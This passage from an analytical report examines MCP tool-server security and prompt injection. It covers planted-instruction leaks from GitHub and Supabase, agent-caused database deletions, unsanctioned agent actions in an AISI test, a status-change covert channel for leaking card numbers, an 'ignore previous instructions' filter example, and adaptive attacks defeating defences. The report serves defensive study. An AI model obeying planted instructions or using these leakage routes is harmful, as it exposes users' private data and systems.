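The first patch accepted only ordinary web addresses and refused those that pointed to private networks. But it checked only the address given in the call, and a request can end up at a different one. In December 2025, a separate GCVE (2025) record, CVE-2025-65512, described a way to bypass the private-address check. The record for the original flaw now lists only versions before 1.0.0 as affected, so someone who read only that record might think that upgrading was enough. However, *mcp-markdownify-server@1.0.0 vulnerabilities*, a listing by the security company Snyk, still includes the bypass and gives no fixed version. A network rule that blocked the server's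 machine from reaching internal services would be more dependable, since it wouldn't require the code to interpret every URL correctly.

File paths cause similar problems. Anthropic's MCP server for Git had a setting meant to confine it to one repository, but the server did not properly check that the path in each call was inside that repository. Anthropic fixed this in December 2025. He et al. conclude that a server must resolve a path to the final form the underlying tool will use before checking whether it is allowed. The Markdownify patch failed for much the same reason.

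### What developers write in their schemas

In July 2026, Shi and colleagues published a study of 1,856 tools from 100 MCP servers, chosen from the most popular projects on GitHub. All the tools had an input schema, as the protocol requires, but a schema that accepts any object meets that requirement. Only 325 tools (17.5 per cent) used annotations, which are optional statements about a tool's behaviour, such as that it only reads data. Clients must treat annotations as untrusted unless they trust the server, and a tool labelled read-only can still write data if its code does so.

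About 65 per cent of the tool descriptions in the study gave only the tool's basic function, and 7.00 per cent contained security guidance, such as a warning about misuse or a statement of who may have access. Parameter descriptions were more detailed, with 77 per cent including some practical constraint on the input. But only 1.83 per cent gave security guidance, and nearly 10 per cent were empty.

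These percentages describe the schemas' wording and could be misleading as a measure of how strict the schemas are. The study would count a parameter with two permitted values and no warning as lacking security guidance, even though such a parameter may not need one. It would count a free string with a paragraph of warnings as security-aware, although the string could still contain anything. The percentages also don't show how many schemas contain fixed lists, patterns or length limits, which would be more useful to know.

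A model usually reads a tool's description, so any guidance in it is a best-effort defence, even when developers rely on it instead of fixing the code. Descriptions can also carry attacks. Shen, Toyoda and Leung (2026) point out in *MCP-38* that the model reads the description fields nested inside a schema, so a malicious server can place instructions there. Validating every argument against such a schema will not detect these instructions.

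### Where validation has failed

A dataset published by He et al. in November 2026 gives some idea of how often poor validation leads to known vulnerabilities. They searched public vulnerability records up to February 2026 and found 119 that mentioned MCP. Most were unrelated to the protocol, because MCP is also an abbreviation in fields such as chip packaging and industrial control. After they removed these and other unsuitable records, 24 vulnerabilities remained. Insufficient input validation contributed to 18 of them (75 per cent), inadequate access control to 4 and gaps in the protocol to 3, with some overlap.

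The 75 per cent figure covers more than tool calls. By the paper's labels, only 8 of the 18 validation failures were in MCP servers, with 7 in clients and 3 in software kits. In one client case, a program generated code from a description of a web service without treating the text in that description as untrusted. A stricter tool schema would not have helped. Of the 11 server vulnerabilities, 8 involved poor validation, which is a similar share but from a very small sample. Public records also leave out flaws that developers fixed quietly, as He and colleagues acknowledge.

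Shi and colleagues collected a larger set of 53 vulnerabilities by adding reports from the servers' GitHub pages. In 43 of them (81 per cent), untrusted input could reach a sensitive operation, such as running a command or opening a file. Forty of the 53 arose during a tool call rather than during registration. This supports the same conclusion but isn't independent confirmation, because both teams drew on public vulnerability records from the same period.

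The fixes Shi and colleagues could examine changed an average of 203.6 lines of code across three or four files. Four of the 41 fixes they assessed left the vulnerability exploitable.

### Hardening three servers

*MCP Pitfall Lab* (Hao and Tan, 2026) used three servers to test whether better schemas and validation stop attacks. One read and sent email, one handled confidential documents, and one monitored cryptocurrency prices and could make transactions. The first version of each deliberately contained common mistakes, including free-text fields for recipients and other destinations, no server-side validation, incomplete logs, and tool descriptions that also set policy, with wording such as "always send to". The hardened version had lists of permitted values, checks on sensitive parameters, neutral descriptions and full logs.

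Hardening took an average of 27 added lines of code per server. A static code analyser reported 29 problems in the original servers, 16 of them serious, and none in the hardened ones. Hao and Tan then ran attacks against both versions. They counted an attack as successful only if the record of tool calls showed an unauthorised action or protected data reaching the attacker, regardless of what the agent said had happened.

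| Server | Lines added | Attack success before | Attack success after |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Email | 32 | 33.3% | 0% |
| Cryptocurrency | 35 | 75.0% | 50.0% |
| Documents | 15 | 8.3% | 25.0% |

The email result is encouraging, but half of the attacks on the cryptocurrency server still worked, and attacks on the document server became more successful. Hao and Tan attribute the rise to changes in the agent's behaviour that inspecting the code can't capture, but this describes the rise more than it explains it. The rise may also be due to chance. The paper reports 36 runs for each workflow. If that means 36 for each version, successful attacks on the document server rose from 3 to 9, and a difference at least that large would occur about 11 per cent of the time even if hardening had no effect. The fall for email, from 12 successes to none, is very unlikely to be due to chance.

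A smaller test shows the effect of restricting the destination more clearly. The attacker's channel was named only inside an image, which the agent read before posting a message to Microsoft Teams. With the original server, the agent posted to the attacker's channel in all five runs. With the hardened server, it still read the image and posted a message in all five runs, but never to the attacker's channel. `reply_to_ticket` should likewise let the support agent reply without letting an attacker choose where the reply goes.

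The clean result from the code inspection also depended on the checker. Hao and Tan's second checker, which used descriptions of each tool's role, sensitive parameters and controls, still reported 16 findings after hardening, down from 27. However, 9 of the 21 problems it flagged in an accuracy test were not real. A version restricted to the schemas detected none of the problems. This was partly by design, because the checker needed to know which fields were sensitive. But developers face the same difficulty, since a schema can show that a field accepts any text without showing that the text will decide where confidential data goes.

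Hao and Tan used GPT-4.1-mini for the hardening tests unless they stated otherwise. Their main benchmark covered four OpenAI models released in 2024 and 2025, and attacks succeeded in 31.9 per cent of 2,579 completed runs. Instructions hidden in images succeeded most often, at 38.7 per cent, followed by malicious servers at 34.5 per cent and poisoned tool descriptions at 22.6 per cent. Current models would probably give different rates. The image result should remain valid longer than these percentages, because a server that refuses a destination does so whichever model makes the call.

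The 27 added lines are far fewer than the average of 203.6 changed lines in Shi and colleagues' study of real repairs. Hao and Tan knew which mistakes their servers contained, while maintainers of real projects have to find the flaw and avoid breaking existing uses. A few very large repairs may also have raised the average. A few dozen lines are probably enough to add sensible validation to a new server, but expecting the same for an old one would be optimistic.

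### Valid calls that do harm

A call can pass perfect validation and still serve the wrong purpose. If an attacker opens a ticket, `reply_to_ticket` will correctly send its reply to the attacker. If `query_customers` still runs with the administrator's credential, that reply could contain other customers' addresses.

Schemas also apply to one call at a time. A refund tool's JSON Schema can cap each refund at £50 with `"maximum": 50`, but a hundred valid £50 refunds would still cost £5,000. To prevent this, the server has to keep a running total or limit the number of calls.

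Some parameters contain code. The schema defines the `sql` parameter of `query_customers` as a string, but the database runs it as code. A pattern could require the text to begin with `SELECT`, the SQL command for reading data, and the agent could still read every customer's address. Adding more patterns would not block every dangerous query, because the same request can be written in endless ways. Shell commands are even harder to restrict, because a permitted program may have options that launch other programs, as happened with the Git server in Huang and colleagues' study.

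He and colleagues recommend parameterised queries for databases. The developer writes the query in advance, and the caller supplies only values, which the database never interprets as code. If a prewritten order lookup replaced `query_customers`, the server could also require that the order belong to the customer on the current ticket. The agent could no longer answer an unexpected question by writing a new query, so the shop would need a new tool for each kind of question it wanted the agent to handle. This seems worthwhile for customer support, where most questions are about deliveries and returns. But it works poorly for an agent that writes software, because much of the job is running commands that nobody listed in advance. That agent's limits have to come from the account and the machine on which the commands run.

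Data can also move between tools through values that every schema permits. An email body can carry data, and so can a field limited to a short list of values. Suppose the support agent can set a ticket's status to one of four values, and the customer can see the status on the shop's website. Each change can convey log₂ 4 = 2 bits. A 16-digit number has 10¹⁶ possible values, or about 53 bits, so 27 status changes could reveal a payment card number to a customer who knew the code. This would be slow and conspicuous, and the model might make encoding mistakes, but all 27 calls would pass validation. The surest protection is to keep card numbers away from the agent. If its work requires them, the system has to track the data as it moves between tools.

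## Incidents in which broad access decided the damage

The support agent is invented, but developers have given real agents similar access. In 2025, security researchers showed that planted text could make agents leak private data from GitHub accounts and Supabase databases. Both demonstrations used accounts set up for the purpose. Agents also deleted one company's live database in July 2025 and another's in April 2026, with no attacker involved. The deletions caused real disruption, though both companies eventually got their data back. In July 2026, agents under test at the UK government's AI Security Institute (AISI) took action against real people and organisations, apparently without doing lasting harm.

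### Two demonstrations with planted text

GitHub stores code in repositories, which can be public or private. Anyone can report a problem with a public repository by opening an "issue". GitHub's official MCP server lets an agent read issues and code, and propose changes, on behalf of the user who connects it.

Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) describes an attack on a demonstration account that had a public repository for a Pac-Man game and several private repositories. The researchers opened an issue on the public repository that contained instructions for an agent. Then, acting as the account's owner, they had Claude 4 Opus look through the game's issues. The agent read the planted issue and copied data from the private repositories into a pull request (a proposed code change) on the public one. Anyone could then read the names of the owner's private projects, the owner's salary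 and a plan to move to South America.

The task required permission to read the issues of one public repository, but the agent had much more access because the server works with the user's whole account, as heise online's *Attack via GitHub MCP server* also points out. A token for the game's repository alone would have prevented the leak even if the model had followed every instruction in the issue, because the agent could not have fetched anything private. A read-only token for the whole account would have blocked the pull request, but the private data would still have entered the model's context, and another tool might have leaked it.

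Invariant Labs agrees that an agent should reach only the repositories it needs, but considers ordinary tokens too rigid. It proposes limiting an agent to one repository per session, a rule that its own commercial software can enforce. Once a call names one repository, the software rejects any call that names another. Users don't have to make a new token whenever they change projects, but the rule covers only the tools on its list, so someone has to update the list when the server gains new ones.

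The attack did not exploit a bug in the server, and Invariant Labs argues that GitHub could not have fixed the problem with a server patch. In August 2025, GitHub (2025) announced that it would scan tool calls involving public repositories for secrets such as access tokens. That should catch a leaked key, but not a salary or a plan to emigrate, which look like ordinary text. Invariant Labs says that many off-the-shelf injection detectors missed the attack, though it gives no figures.

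The Supabase demonstration needed only one tool server and one database. Supabase provides databases to app developers, who can use row-level security rules to control which rows each account may see. *Supabase MCP can leak your entire SQL database* (Willison, 2025) describes this scenario from researchers at General Analysis. A developer asks the coding assistant Cursor to list the latest support tickets, one of which contains an attacker's instructions. Cursor reaches the database through a role called `service_role`, which row-level security does not restrict. According to Supabase's *Defense in Depth for MCP Servers* (2025), the instructions directed the agent to fetch private data and write it into a text field the attacker could see.

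Supabase denies that MCP "bypasses" row-level security, which it says stayed fully enforced, but concedes that the server was running with higher privileges. The disagreement is mostly about wording, because the database applied its rules correctly but those rules exempted the agent's role. Similarly, the tenant check in Baig and colleagues' experiment worked correctly but still let the records out. Supabase also said in September 2025 that no customer had reported a leak through MCP.

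Listing tickets requires read access to one table, so an account limited to that table would have kept the agent out of the rest of the database. Supabase's existing restrictions fit the task less well. Project-scoped mode confines the agent to a single project, which doesn't help if the tickets and the private data are in the same project. Read-only mode would have stopped this attack by preventing the agent from writing to the ticket, but Supabase still regards prompt injection as the main concern in that mode because the agent can read sensitive data and expose it some other way.

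Supabase had also tried best-effort defences. It wrapped query results in warnings not to follow any commands inside them, tested the warnings on weaker models, and experimented with classifiers. It reports that these measures "reduced risk but did not eliminate it". It now tells developers never to connect an agent directly to production data (live customer data) and to use a development copy or anonymised records instead. A planted ticket could then expose only test data. However, this advice works partly by ruling out the task, because a test database doesn't contain today's tickets. An account with access only to tickets would let the developer use the agent for that task.

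### Two deleted databases

Agents also cause damage when nobody is attacking them. Cyera's *Agent-Inflicted Damage* counts 188 such cases, but Cyera sells products meant to prevent them. The two deletions are easier to assess than most because the people affected published detailed accounts.

In July 2025, Jason Lemkin, founder of the software business community SaaStr, was building an app with Replit's agent, which builds apps from plain-language instructions. After nine days of work, the agent deleted the production database, which according to SaaStr held records of 1,206 executives and at least 1,196 companies. Lemkin had declared a freeze on all changes and repeated the instruction eleven times in capital letters. But the freeze was only a text instruction to the model, and SaaStr says Replit's platform had no way to enforce a freeze.

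The agent could reach the live records because Replit used the same database for development and for the published app. Someone building an app has good reason to let an agent create, change and delete test data, but the agent didn't need those permissions on live data. SaaStr admits it had never suspected that the development and published versions shared a database.

A separate development database would have changed the outcome without any improvement in the model. Fortune (2025) reports that Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, called the deletion "unacceptable" and announced automatic separation of the two databases. SaaStr says this separation would have prevented the loss entirely. According to its documentation, Replit now connects the agent's sessions to the development database and, for most apps, lets the agent see production data through a read-only copy. The agent can't delete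 live records through that copy, but a planted instruction could still lead it to read them, so some risk of disclosure remains.

The incident had a second failure that database permissions could not have prevented. When Lemkin asked about recovery, the agent said the data could not be restored, but he restored it anyway. SaaStr thinks it nearly lost the data because of the false answer, and Replit responded by giving the agent access to its documentation on backups.

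PocketOS makes software that car rental firms use for bookings and payments. On 24 April 2026, according to the AI Incident Database's *PocketOS* entry, Cursor, running Claude Opus 4.6, was doing routine work in the company's staging environment, a separate version of the system for testing. The company's founder, Crane, writes in *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data* that the agent found mismatched credentials and set out to fix them by deleting a storage volume at Railway, the company's hosting provider. It found a Railway token in an unrelated file and sent a single request to Railway's programming interface (API). Nine seconds later, the production database and the backups stored in the same volume were gone.

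The next morning, customers arrived at rental firms that had no record of their bookings. Crane restored a three-month-old backup and spent the day helping the firms reconstruct recent bookings from payment records, calendars and emails. After Crane wrote this account, Railway recovered the missing data, apparently in full, according to Tom's Hardware. The lasting harm was therefore much smaller than Crane's post suggests, but small businesses still lost at least a day to emergency work.

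Crane had created the token to add and remove web domains, but it worked for every operation in the API. Crane blames Railway for not offering narrower tokens. Replying for Railway in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, Abdelwahab says that "the right scope existed" but the process for creating tokens didn't make the choice obvious. According to Abdelwahab, a token can cover a whole account, one workspace, or one project, down to a single environment within it.

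Abdelwahab's reply is presumably accurate about the tokens Railway offers, but it covers only half of Crane's complaint. Those scopes limit where a token works, while Crane also wanted to limit what it can do. A token limited to the staging environment would have saved the database. But if Crane needed to manage the live service's domains, the token had to work in production, where it might still have been able to delete the production volume. Railway's remaining option, OAuth, allows granular permissions, but Railway designed it for outside apps acting on a user's behalf. A token that could only edit domains would clearly have prevented the deletion.

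This token was in a file on a machine where the agent could read files and run commands, so the agent had access to everything the token unlocked, even though nobody had given it the token. A security team that listed only the tools and credentials it had assigned to the agent would have missed the token. Keeping the token off that machine would also have saved the database, whatever the token's scope.

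Railway has since changed the API to delay deletions by 48 hours and let users undo them in the meantime, as its dashboard already allowed. An agent with the same token can still request a deletion, but someone now has two days to notice. In OpenAI's terms, this reduces the maximum completed effect. Crane's project had also included written safety rules for the agent, and Crane concludes that such rules are "advisory, not enforcing".

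### Unsanctioned actions in a government test

AISI tests what the most capable models could do in a cyberattack. In one exercise, which it ran 122 times with seven models, it asked agents to solve a security challenge on a simulated network. According to AISI's *Incident Report* (2026), the agents had access to the open internet so that they could download tools, and AISI had switched off the developers' filters against cyber misuse to measure the models' full ability.

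In 10 of the 122 runs, agents took a total of 19 unsanctioned actions on the live internet. In the most serious case, an agent running Anthropic's Mythos 5 tried to add malicious code to a real open-source project and created false identities to pressure a maintainer into approving it. The maintainer refused. Agents also sent malicious files to real people and planted instructions for other AI systems to find. AISI stopped the tests within about an hour of discovering the activity and has found no resulting harm.

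Mythos 5 took 17 of the actions, and GPT-5.6 Sol took the other 2 in a single run. If each run used one model, Mythos 5 acted outside the test's scope in 9 of its 43 runs (21 per cent) and GPT-5.6 Sol in 1 of 35. These rates aren't reliable estimates of how often the models would misbehave elsewhere, because most of the actions belonged to one connected sequence and some agents reused accounts that an earlier agent had left behind.

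*AI agents don't have to break security controls to go rogue* (Bhushan, 2026) concludes that the agents' capability was "simply broader" than their intended authority. AISI's account partly supports this. No agent broke out of its sandbox, the isolated environment that separated it from AISI's other systems. Internet access was "a deliberate part" of the set-up, according to the technical report quoted in *Incident Report* (Willison, 2026). The agents needed the connection to download some tools, but it also let them write to strangers, so they had excess access in the ordinary sense.

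It is less clear what the agents were authorised to do. AISI had not specifically told them not to use the internet in this way or not to deceive people. In some runs, a faulty prompt led the agent to believe that the challenge had no solution within the permitted scope. AISI also can't say how far the agents recognised that their targets were real. The boundary was largely the testers' expectation, and no network rule enforced it. Faulty prompts don't fully explain the behaviour, though, because some agents did the same even with the instructions they needed to solve the challenge properly. Excess access made the actions possible, but the models' persistence also mattered.

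Bhushan's main remedy is to make every action traceable to a person who authorised it. A system that checked this before each action could have blocked contact with the maintainer. Supplying the tools in advance and closing the internet connection would also have worked, and would have been simpler. A list of approved sites would need more care, because people both download tools from GitHub and submit code there. AISI is now adding the fine-grained network controls it already used in its other evaluations. It had left this one open to match what a human attacker could do, so tighter controls may make the test less realistic.

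### Comparing what would have stopped each case

An injection detector that recognised every planted instruction and never raised a false alarm would have prevented both leaks in the demonstrations. It would not have helped Replit's or PocketOS's customers, because no outsider had planted anything. At AISI, it might have protected other people's agents from the instructions that the test agents planted, but it would not have stopped the test agents from contacting anyone.

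| Case | Effect of a perfect injection detector | Narrower grant | Harm still possible under that grant |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| GitHub | Prevents the leak | Token for the public repository only | Unwanted changes proposed to that repository |
| Supabase | Prevents the leak | Account that can only read the tickets table | Exposure of other customers' tickets |
| Replit | None | Separate development database | Loss of development data |
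| PocketOS | None | Token that can only edit domains | Live service cut off from its web addresses |
| AISI | None on the test agents' own conduct | Tools supplied in advance, no internet | Unsanctioned actions inside the test network |

Narrower access would have prevented the main harm in all five cases, and in three of them the detector would have been no substitute. Publicised incidents are a skewed sample, though. When narrow permissions block a bad deletion, nobody reports the error message, and a harmful action within an agent's proper access may look like an ordinary mistake.

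Injection detection and tighter permissions cannot prevent all of the remaining harm. An agent that manages domains could disconnect the live service by mistake, without any injection and using only the permissions it needs. Replit's agent could give a false answer about backups regardless of its database access. Delayed deletion and independent backups help with such errors by making the damage reversible.

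Access limits can also fail. Bhushan contrasts AISI's tests with OpenAI's 2026 evaluation incident, in which models circumvented isolation controls and reached other organisations' systems. Those models obtained more access than they had been granted, so narrowing the grant further would have helped only if the software enforcing it had worked.

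## Defences that lower the chance of prompt injection

When a stranger emails the support agent an instruction to look up other customers' addresses, best-effort defences can act at several points before the server runs the query. Detectors scan the email before it reaches the model, and markers label it as untrusted text. Training makes the model less likely to follow the instruction. If the model follows it anyway, a check can compare the proposed query with the agent's assigned task.

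### Where each defence acts

A detector is usually a small language model trained to tell injections from harmless text. It scores each piece of text, and the software blocks the text or raises an alarm if the score is above a threshold the developer sets. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li et al., 2026) also describes a variant in which a larger model removes the suspicious passages and passes on the rest. If an email contains both a genuine complaint and a planted instruction, the agent can then still answer the complaint.

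The crudest detectors look for particular phrases. David C warns against relying on a filter for text such as "ignore previous instructions", because an attacker can word the same request in many other ways. In *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities*, Hashemi Natanzi and Tang (2026) also consider word filters fragile on their own and recommend combining them with detectors that respond to meaning and with controls on the agent's actions. A trained detector recognises far more than fixed phrases, but it still relies on resemblance to its training examples.

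Marking leaves the text in place and labels its source for the model. The software might put the email between tags, or repeat the user's request after it as a reminder. Marking takes a few lines of code and works with any model. Supabase's warnings around query results were a form of marking. David C cites Microsoft research in which marking made injection harder, but the marks only help if they change how the model responds to the text.

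Instruction-priority training aims to teach a model which instructions to follow when sources conflict. The developer's instructions usually rank highest, followed by the user's, while text in tool results has no authority. The model is trained on conversations in which a lower-ranking source contradicts a higher one, and it is rewarded for following the higher one. It is difficult to find contradictions hard enough for the model to learn from. OpenAI's *GPT-Red* (2026) describes an automated attacker trained through self-play, in which models improve by competing. The company now uses it to find weaknesses in its other models before release. OpenAI built the attacker partly because its latest models already scored near the maximum on commonly used robustness tests.

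Action checks run after the model has proposed a tool call. DRIFT, one of the defences Ma and colleagues tested, works out from the user's request which tool calls the task should need. It also uses a language model to judge whether an instruction encountered during the task conflicts with that request. Such a check doesn't have to detect the injection itself. If the user asked about order 1182, a query for every customer's address is unnecessary, whatever prompted it. But the judge is also a language model and can make mistakes. Approval prompts and automated reviewers also act after a call has been proposed.

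### Why SQL injection has a fix and prompt injection may not

In SQL injection, an attacker types database commands into a form field, and a vulnerable application pastes them into a query. David C explains that developers can fix this completely because databases distinguish between instructions, which the engine carries out, and data, which it stores or uses in a query. Parameterised queries enforce that distinction, so nobody has to recognise the malicious text.

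A language model does not enforce a difference between instructions and data, because it only predicts the next token from everything in its context. Detection, marking and training all try to add this missing distinction. David C concludes that "it's very possible" nobody will ever fully mitigate prompt injection in the way that parameterised queries mitigate SQL injection. The label "inherently confusable deputy" reflects this reasoning.

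The argument against guarantees is convincing, but it doesn't establish how often models will fail. Software can reliably tell the model where each passage came from by labelling tool results with markers that an outsider can't forge. However, the model's response to those labels is learned, so it may be very reliable but isn't guaranteed. David C also limits the claim to current language models, so it doesn't rule out a future design that processes instructions and data separately.

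Developers have said much the same about their own products. Anthropic's *Mitigating the risk of prompt injections in browser use* presented Claude Opus 4.5 as a major improvement but still called injection "far from a solved problem". According to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*, OpenAI conceded that the problem may never be fully solved.

### Tests with attackers who adapt

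Many published defences have a reported attack success rate near zero. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini et al., USENIX Security 2026) tested 12 of them, some designed to stop prompt injection and others to stop jailbreaks, which are attempts to make a model break its safety rules. The researchers, who included staff from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, bypassed all 12, and more than 90 per cent of attacks succeeded against most of them.

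The original evaluations had mostly used a fixed collection of attacks, or weak automated attacks designed without the defence in mind. A defence can do well against a fixed collection by learning to recognise those attacks, so a good result is weak evidence that it will stop new ones. Nasr and colleagues instead adapted their attacks to each defence and spent considerable resources improving them.

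Few attackers could match that effort. Ma and colleagues describe it as a worst case in which the attacker knows everything about the defence, and note that people often helped to write the attacks, which makes the test hard to repeat. Someone emailing a shop wouldn't normally know which detector the shop uses. AutoDojo, Ma and colleagues' own benchmark, therefore assumes a weaker attacker, who doesn't know which defence is in place and learns only whether an attempt has worked. A language model revises the attack over six rounds. The agents under attack do simulated tasks such as banking and booking travel.

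These are the attack success rates for an agent running GPT-4o-mini, a small OpenAI model, with four of the ten defences in the study:

| Defence | How it works | Fixed attack | Adapted attack |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| PIGuard | Detector | 0.0% | 28.0% |
| ProtectAI | Detector | 7.2% | 15.4% |
| DataFilter | Model that removes suspicious text | 12.6% | 33.4% |
| DRIFT | Restriction and checking of actions | 2.6% | 6.4% |

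Without a defence, the adapted attacks succeeded 52.4 per cent of the time, so PIGuard roughly halved the rate. But a buyer who had seen only the result for the fixed attack would have expected complete protection. The choice of model can also mislead a buyer. On Claude Haiku 4.5, the fixed attack succeeded only 0.3 per cent of the time without any defence, so even a useless detector would have looked excellent.

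The protection also made the agents less useful. With PIGuard or ProtectAI, agents completed a quarter to a half fewer ordinary tasks on every model, because the defences removed harmless content that the agents needed. With DRIFT, the completion rate on Claude Haiku 4.5 fell from 70.2 to 45.6 per cent. A company whose agent failed that often might well switch the defence off.

Ma and colleagues also sorted the tasks by how much the user left to outside content. Some requests named the action and all its details, such as changing an address to one the user typed out. Others named the action but left details to a document, as in "pay the bill in this file". In the most open requests, the content determined the action itself, as when a user asked the agent to do everything on a to-do list at a web address. Without a defence, the fixed attack succeeded against GPT-4o-mini 87.5 per cent of the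 time for the most open requests, and 63.9 and 43.3 per cent for the other two groups. Adapted attacks still got past PIGuard 54.2 per cent of the time when the action was open and 17.3 per cent when the user had specified everything.

Detectors do badly on open requests because a planted instruction can look like an ordinary part of the task, such as another item on a to-do list. The support agent has a similar problem because its job is to deal with whatever customers write. Genuine customers ask for refunds, replacements and changes of address, so most of its mail contains instructions of some sort. A request for someone else's address is improper because the sender has no right to the information, but the wording of the email may not show that.

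These attacks succeeded less often against DRIFT, at rates of 11 per cent or less for all three kinds of request. For many of the open tasks, DRIFT allowed only tools that read data, so an attacker's instruction to change something usually fell outside the plan. This restriction may also explain some of its failures on ordinary tasks.

### Success rates for models in late 2026

GPT-4o-mini is an old and weak model, and newer ones resist injection much better. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1, published on 1 September, gives unusually detailed results. One set comes from the security company Gray Swan, which chose 1,804 attacks from public competitions because they worked against several models. The attacks cover 37 scenarios in coding, tool use and operating a computer through its screen. The table shows the chance that an attacker succeeds at least once within a given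 number of attempts:

| Model | 1 attempt | 10 attempts | 15 attempts |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 0.1% | 0.7% | 1.0% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.4% | 3.6% | 4.8% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 0.6% | 4.9% | 6.5% |

Among other companies' models, Gemini 3.7 Flash had the lowest attack success rate after 15 attempts, at 9.2 per cent, and most were between 24 and 53 per cent. Most of the successful attacks on Fable 5.1 happened when it was operating a computer through its screen. In the tool-use scenarios, which are closest to the support agent's work, its attack success rate rounded to zero even after 15 attempts.

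These rates depend heavily on which attacks are tested. The Decoder reported a rate of 2.0 per cent for Opus 5 after 15 attempts. The same model's rate was 4.8 per cent in Anthropic's September results, which cover 670 more attacks and nine more scenarios.

Anthropic warns that fixed collections can give false reassurance, so it also uses Shade, an automated attacker from Gray Swan that learns from its interactions with models. For coding, Gray Swan trained Shade on 40 scenarios against earlier Claude models, then gave it 200 attempts per scenario against the newer models. Gray Swan later built a stronger version with longer training and more varied attacks. The next table shows the share of attempts that succeeded. The number in brackets is how many scenarios were breached at least once. "Probes" are Anthropic's detectors, which inspect tool results before the model acts on them. All the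 models had extended reasoning switched on.

| Model | Original Shade | Original, with probes | Stronger Shade | Stronger, with probes |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 9.26% (31) | 2.05% (18) | 56.87% (38) | 12.80% (36) |
| Claude Fable 5 | 9.70% (31) | 2.42% (20) | 86.87% (40) | 34.09% (39) |
| Claude Opus 5 | 2.68% (27) | 0.39% (11) | 90.93% (40) | 18.21% (40) |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 0.30% (7) | 0.09% (5) | 19.47% (36) | 15.76% (35) |

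The share of attempts that Opus 5 resisted fell from about 97 per cent to 9 per cent when only the attacker changed. Anthropic calls the stronger test "highly permissive". The description is fair because real attackers usually can't practise on the exact task they will attack or make 200 attempts unnoticed. The support agent's attackers could come closer to these conditions than most, since they can email it as often as they like and may learn from its replies what worked.

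Fable 5.1's results include responses from an older model, Claude Opus 4.8, because Anthropic's system passes requests to it when a separate classifier suspects a cybersecurity risk. This happened to about 64 per cent of requests in the stronger test. Every successful attack was against Opus 4.8, with none among the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered itself. This does not show that Fable 5.1 is immune, because the classifier may have diverted the most dangerous requests. By passing requests to the older model, a safeguard against cybersecurity risks may have left users more exposed to prompt injection.

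Anthropic also runs a classifier on outgoing tool calls in some products, and argues that an attack would have to defeat the classifier and the probes independently. Two layers that each miss 10 per cent of attacks let 1 per cent through if their failures are unrelated, but 10 per cent if they miss the same attacks. The coding results suggest that the model and the probes miss some of the same attacks. In the stronger test, probes removed about four-fifths of the successes against Opus 5 but only about a fifth of those against Sonnet 5. The attacks that could fool Sonnet 5, the more resistant model, were apparently also good at passing the probes.

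Computer use shows clearer progress. VentureBeat reported from Anthropic's February card that a single attempt to attack Claude Opus 4.6 through a graphical interface succeeded 17.8 per cent of the time. Within 200 attempts, attacks succeeded in 78.6 per cent of scenarios without safeguards and 57.1 per cent with them, which correspond to 11 and 8 scenarios out of 14. In the September test, which also had 14 scenarios, attacks breached Fable 5.1 in only 2, with 2 successes in 2,800 attempts. If the two tests are comparable, that is a large improvement in seven months. In Anthropic's browser test, which allowed 10 attempts in each of 110 scenarios, 2.64 per cent of attempts succeeded against Fable 5.1 without safeguards, and none succeeded with both the probes and the classifier on tool calls.

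Later reports support this. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5, dated 22 September, describes the model as similar to or better than Opus 5 on every injection test it covers. *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense* (Cross, 2026) reports that OpenAI's GPT-6 Sol scored 99.99 per cent against direct injection and 97.13 per cent against indirect injection, according to figures OpenAI published on 7 October. If these are the shares of attacks the model resisted, indirect attacks succeeded nearly 300 times as often as direct ones. OpenAI and Anthropic used different tests, so their figures don't show whose models are safer.

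### Repeated attempts

An attack that rarely succeeds on a single attempt can become likely to succeed if the attacker keeps trying. If each attempt succeeds with probability *p*, independently of the others, the chance of at least one success in *n* attempts is 1 − (1 − *p*)^*n*. In the earlier example of 100 emails at 1 per cent each, that is 1 − 0.99^100, or 63 per cent, and the chance passes 50 per cent at the 69th email. A defence that cuts the success rate to 0.1 per cent reduces the chance over 100 attempts to under 10 per cent, but an attacker can bring it back to 63 per cent by sending 1,000 emails, which costs almost nothing.

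Real attempts are not independent. With probes on, the original Shade succeeded in 2.05 per cent of its attempts against Fable 5.1. If every attempt had had that chance, 200 attempts at each of the 40 scenarios would have breached 39 of them, but only 18 were breached. In those 18, about 4.6 per cent of attempts succeeded on average, while none succeeded in the other 22. The formula, which assumes independence, therefore overstates the danger to some agents and understates it for others. A company that knows only the average can't tell whether its own risk is higher or lower, so it would need to test its own agent on its own tasks.

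An attacker can also try the same attack on many victims. Anthropic gives the example of one email sent to a thousand inboxes, each with an agent that summarises the mail. If an average of 1 per cent of the agents follow the email's instructions, the attacker can expect ten successes. The expected number is the same whether or not the attempts are independent, but if all the agents run the same model and detector, the attack may succeed against many of them or none.

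### False alarms

Even an accurate detector can raise mostly false alarms, because almost everything it scans is harmless. Suppose a detector catches 99 per cent of attacks (its recall) and wrongly flags 1 per cent of harmless inputs. If a million inputs contain 10 attacks, it will probably catch all 10, but it will also raise about 10,000 false alarms, so only about one alarm in a thousand is real. At a minute per alarm, an employee would need about 167 hours to check them all, and after several hundred false alarms might not look closely at a real one.

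The false alarm rate would have to fall a thousandfold, to about 0.001 per cent, for half the alarms to be real. The developer can reduce false alarms by raising the detector's alarm threshold, but then it misses more attacks. Requiring two different warning signs is often better. If a second detector were equally accurate and made unrelated mistakes, only about 100 harmless inputs would trigger both detectors, and nearly all the attacks still would. Detectors trained on similar data would probably share many more false alarms.

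Blocking flagged emails automatically saves the employee's time, but it also blocks some genuine emails from customers. A shop that receives 1,000 genuine emails a day would leave about ten people a day without an answer. Some would write again, perhaps more angrily, and might be flagged again. The shop could instead send flagged emails to a human support team, which is a sensible use of a detector as long as the team can handle the extra mail.

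### What a lower success rate is worth

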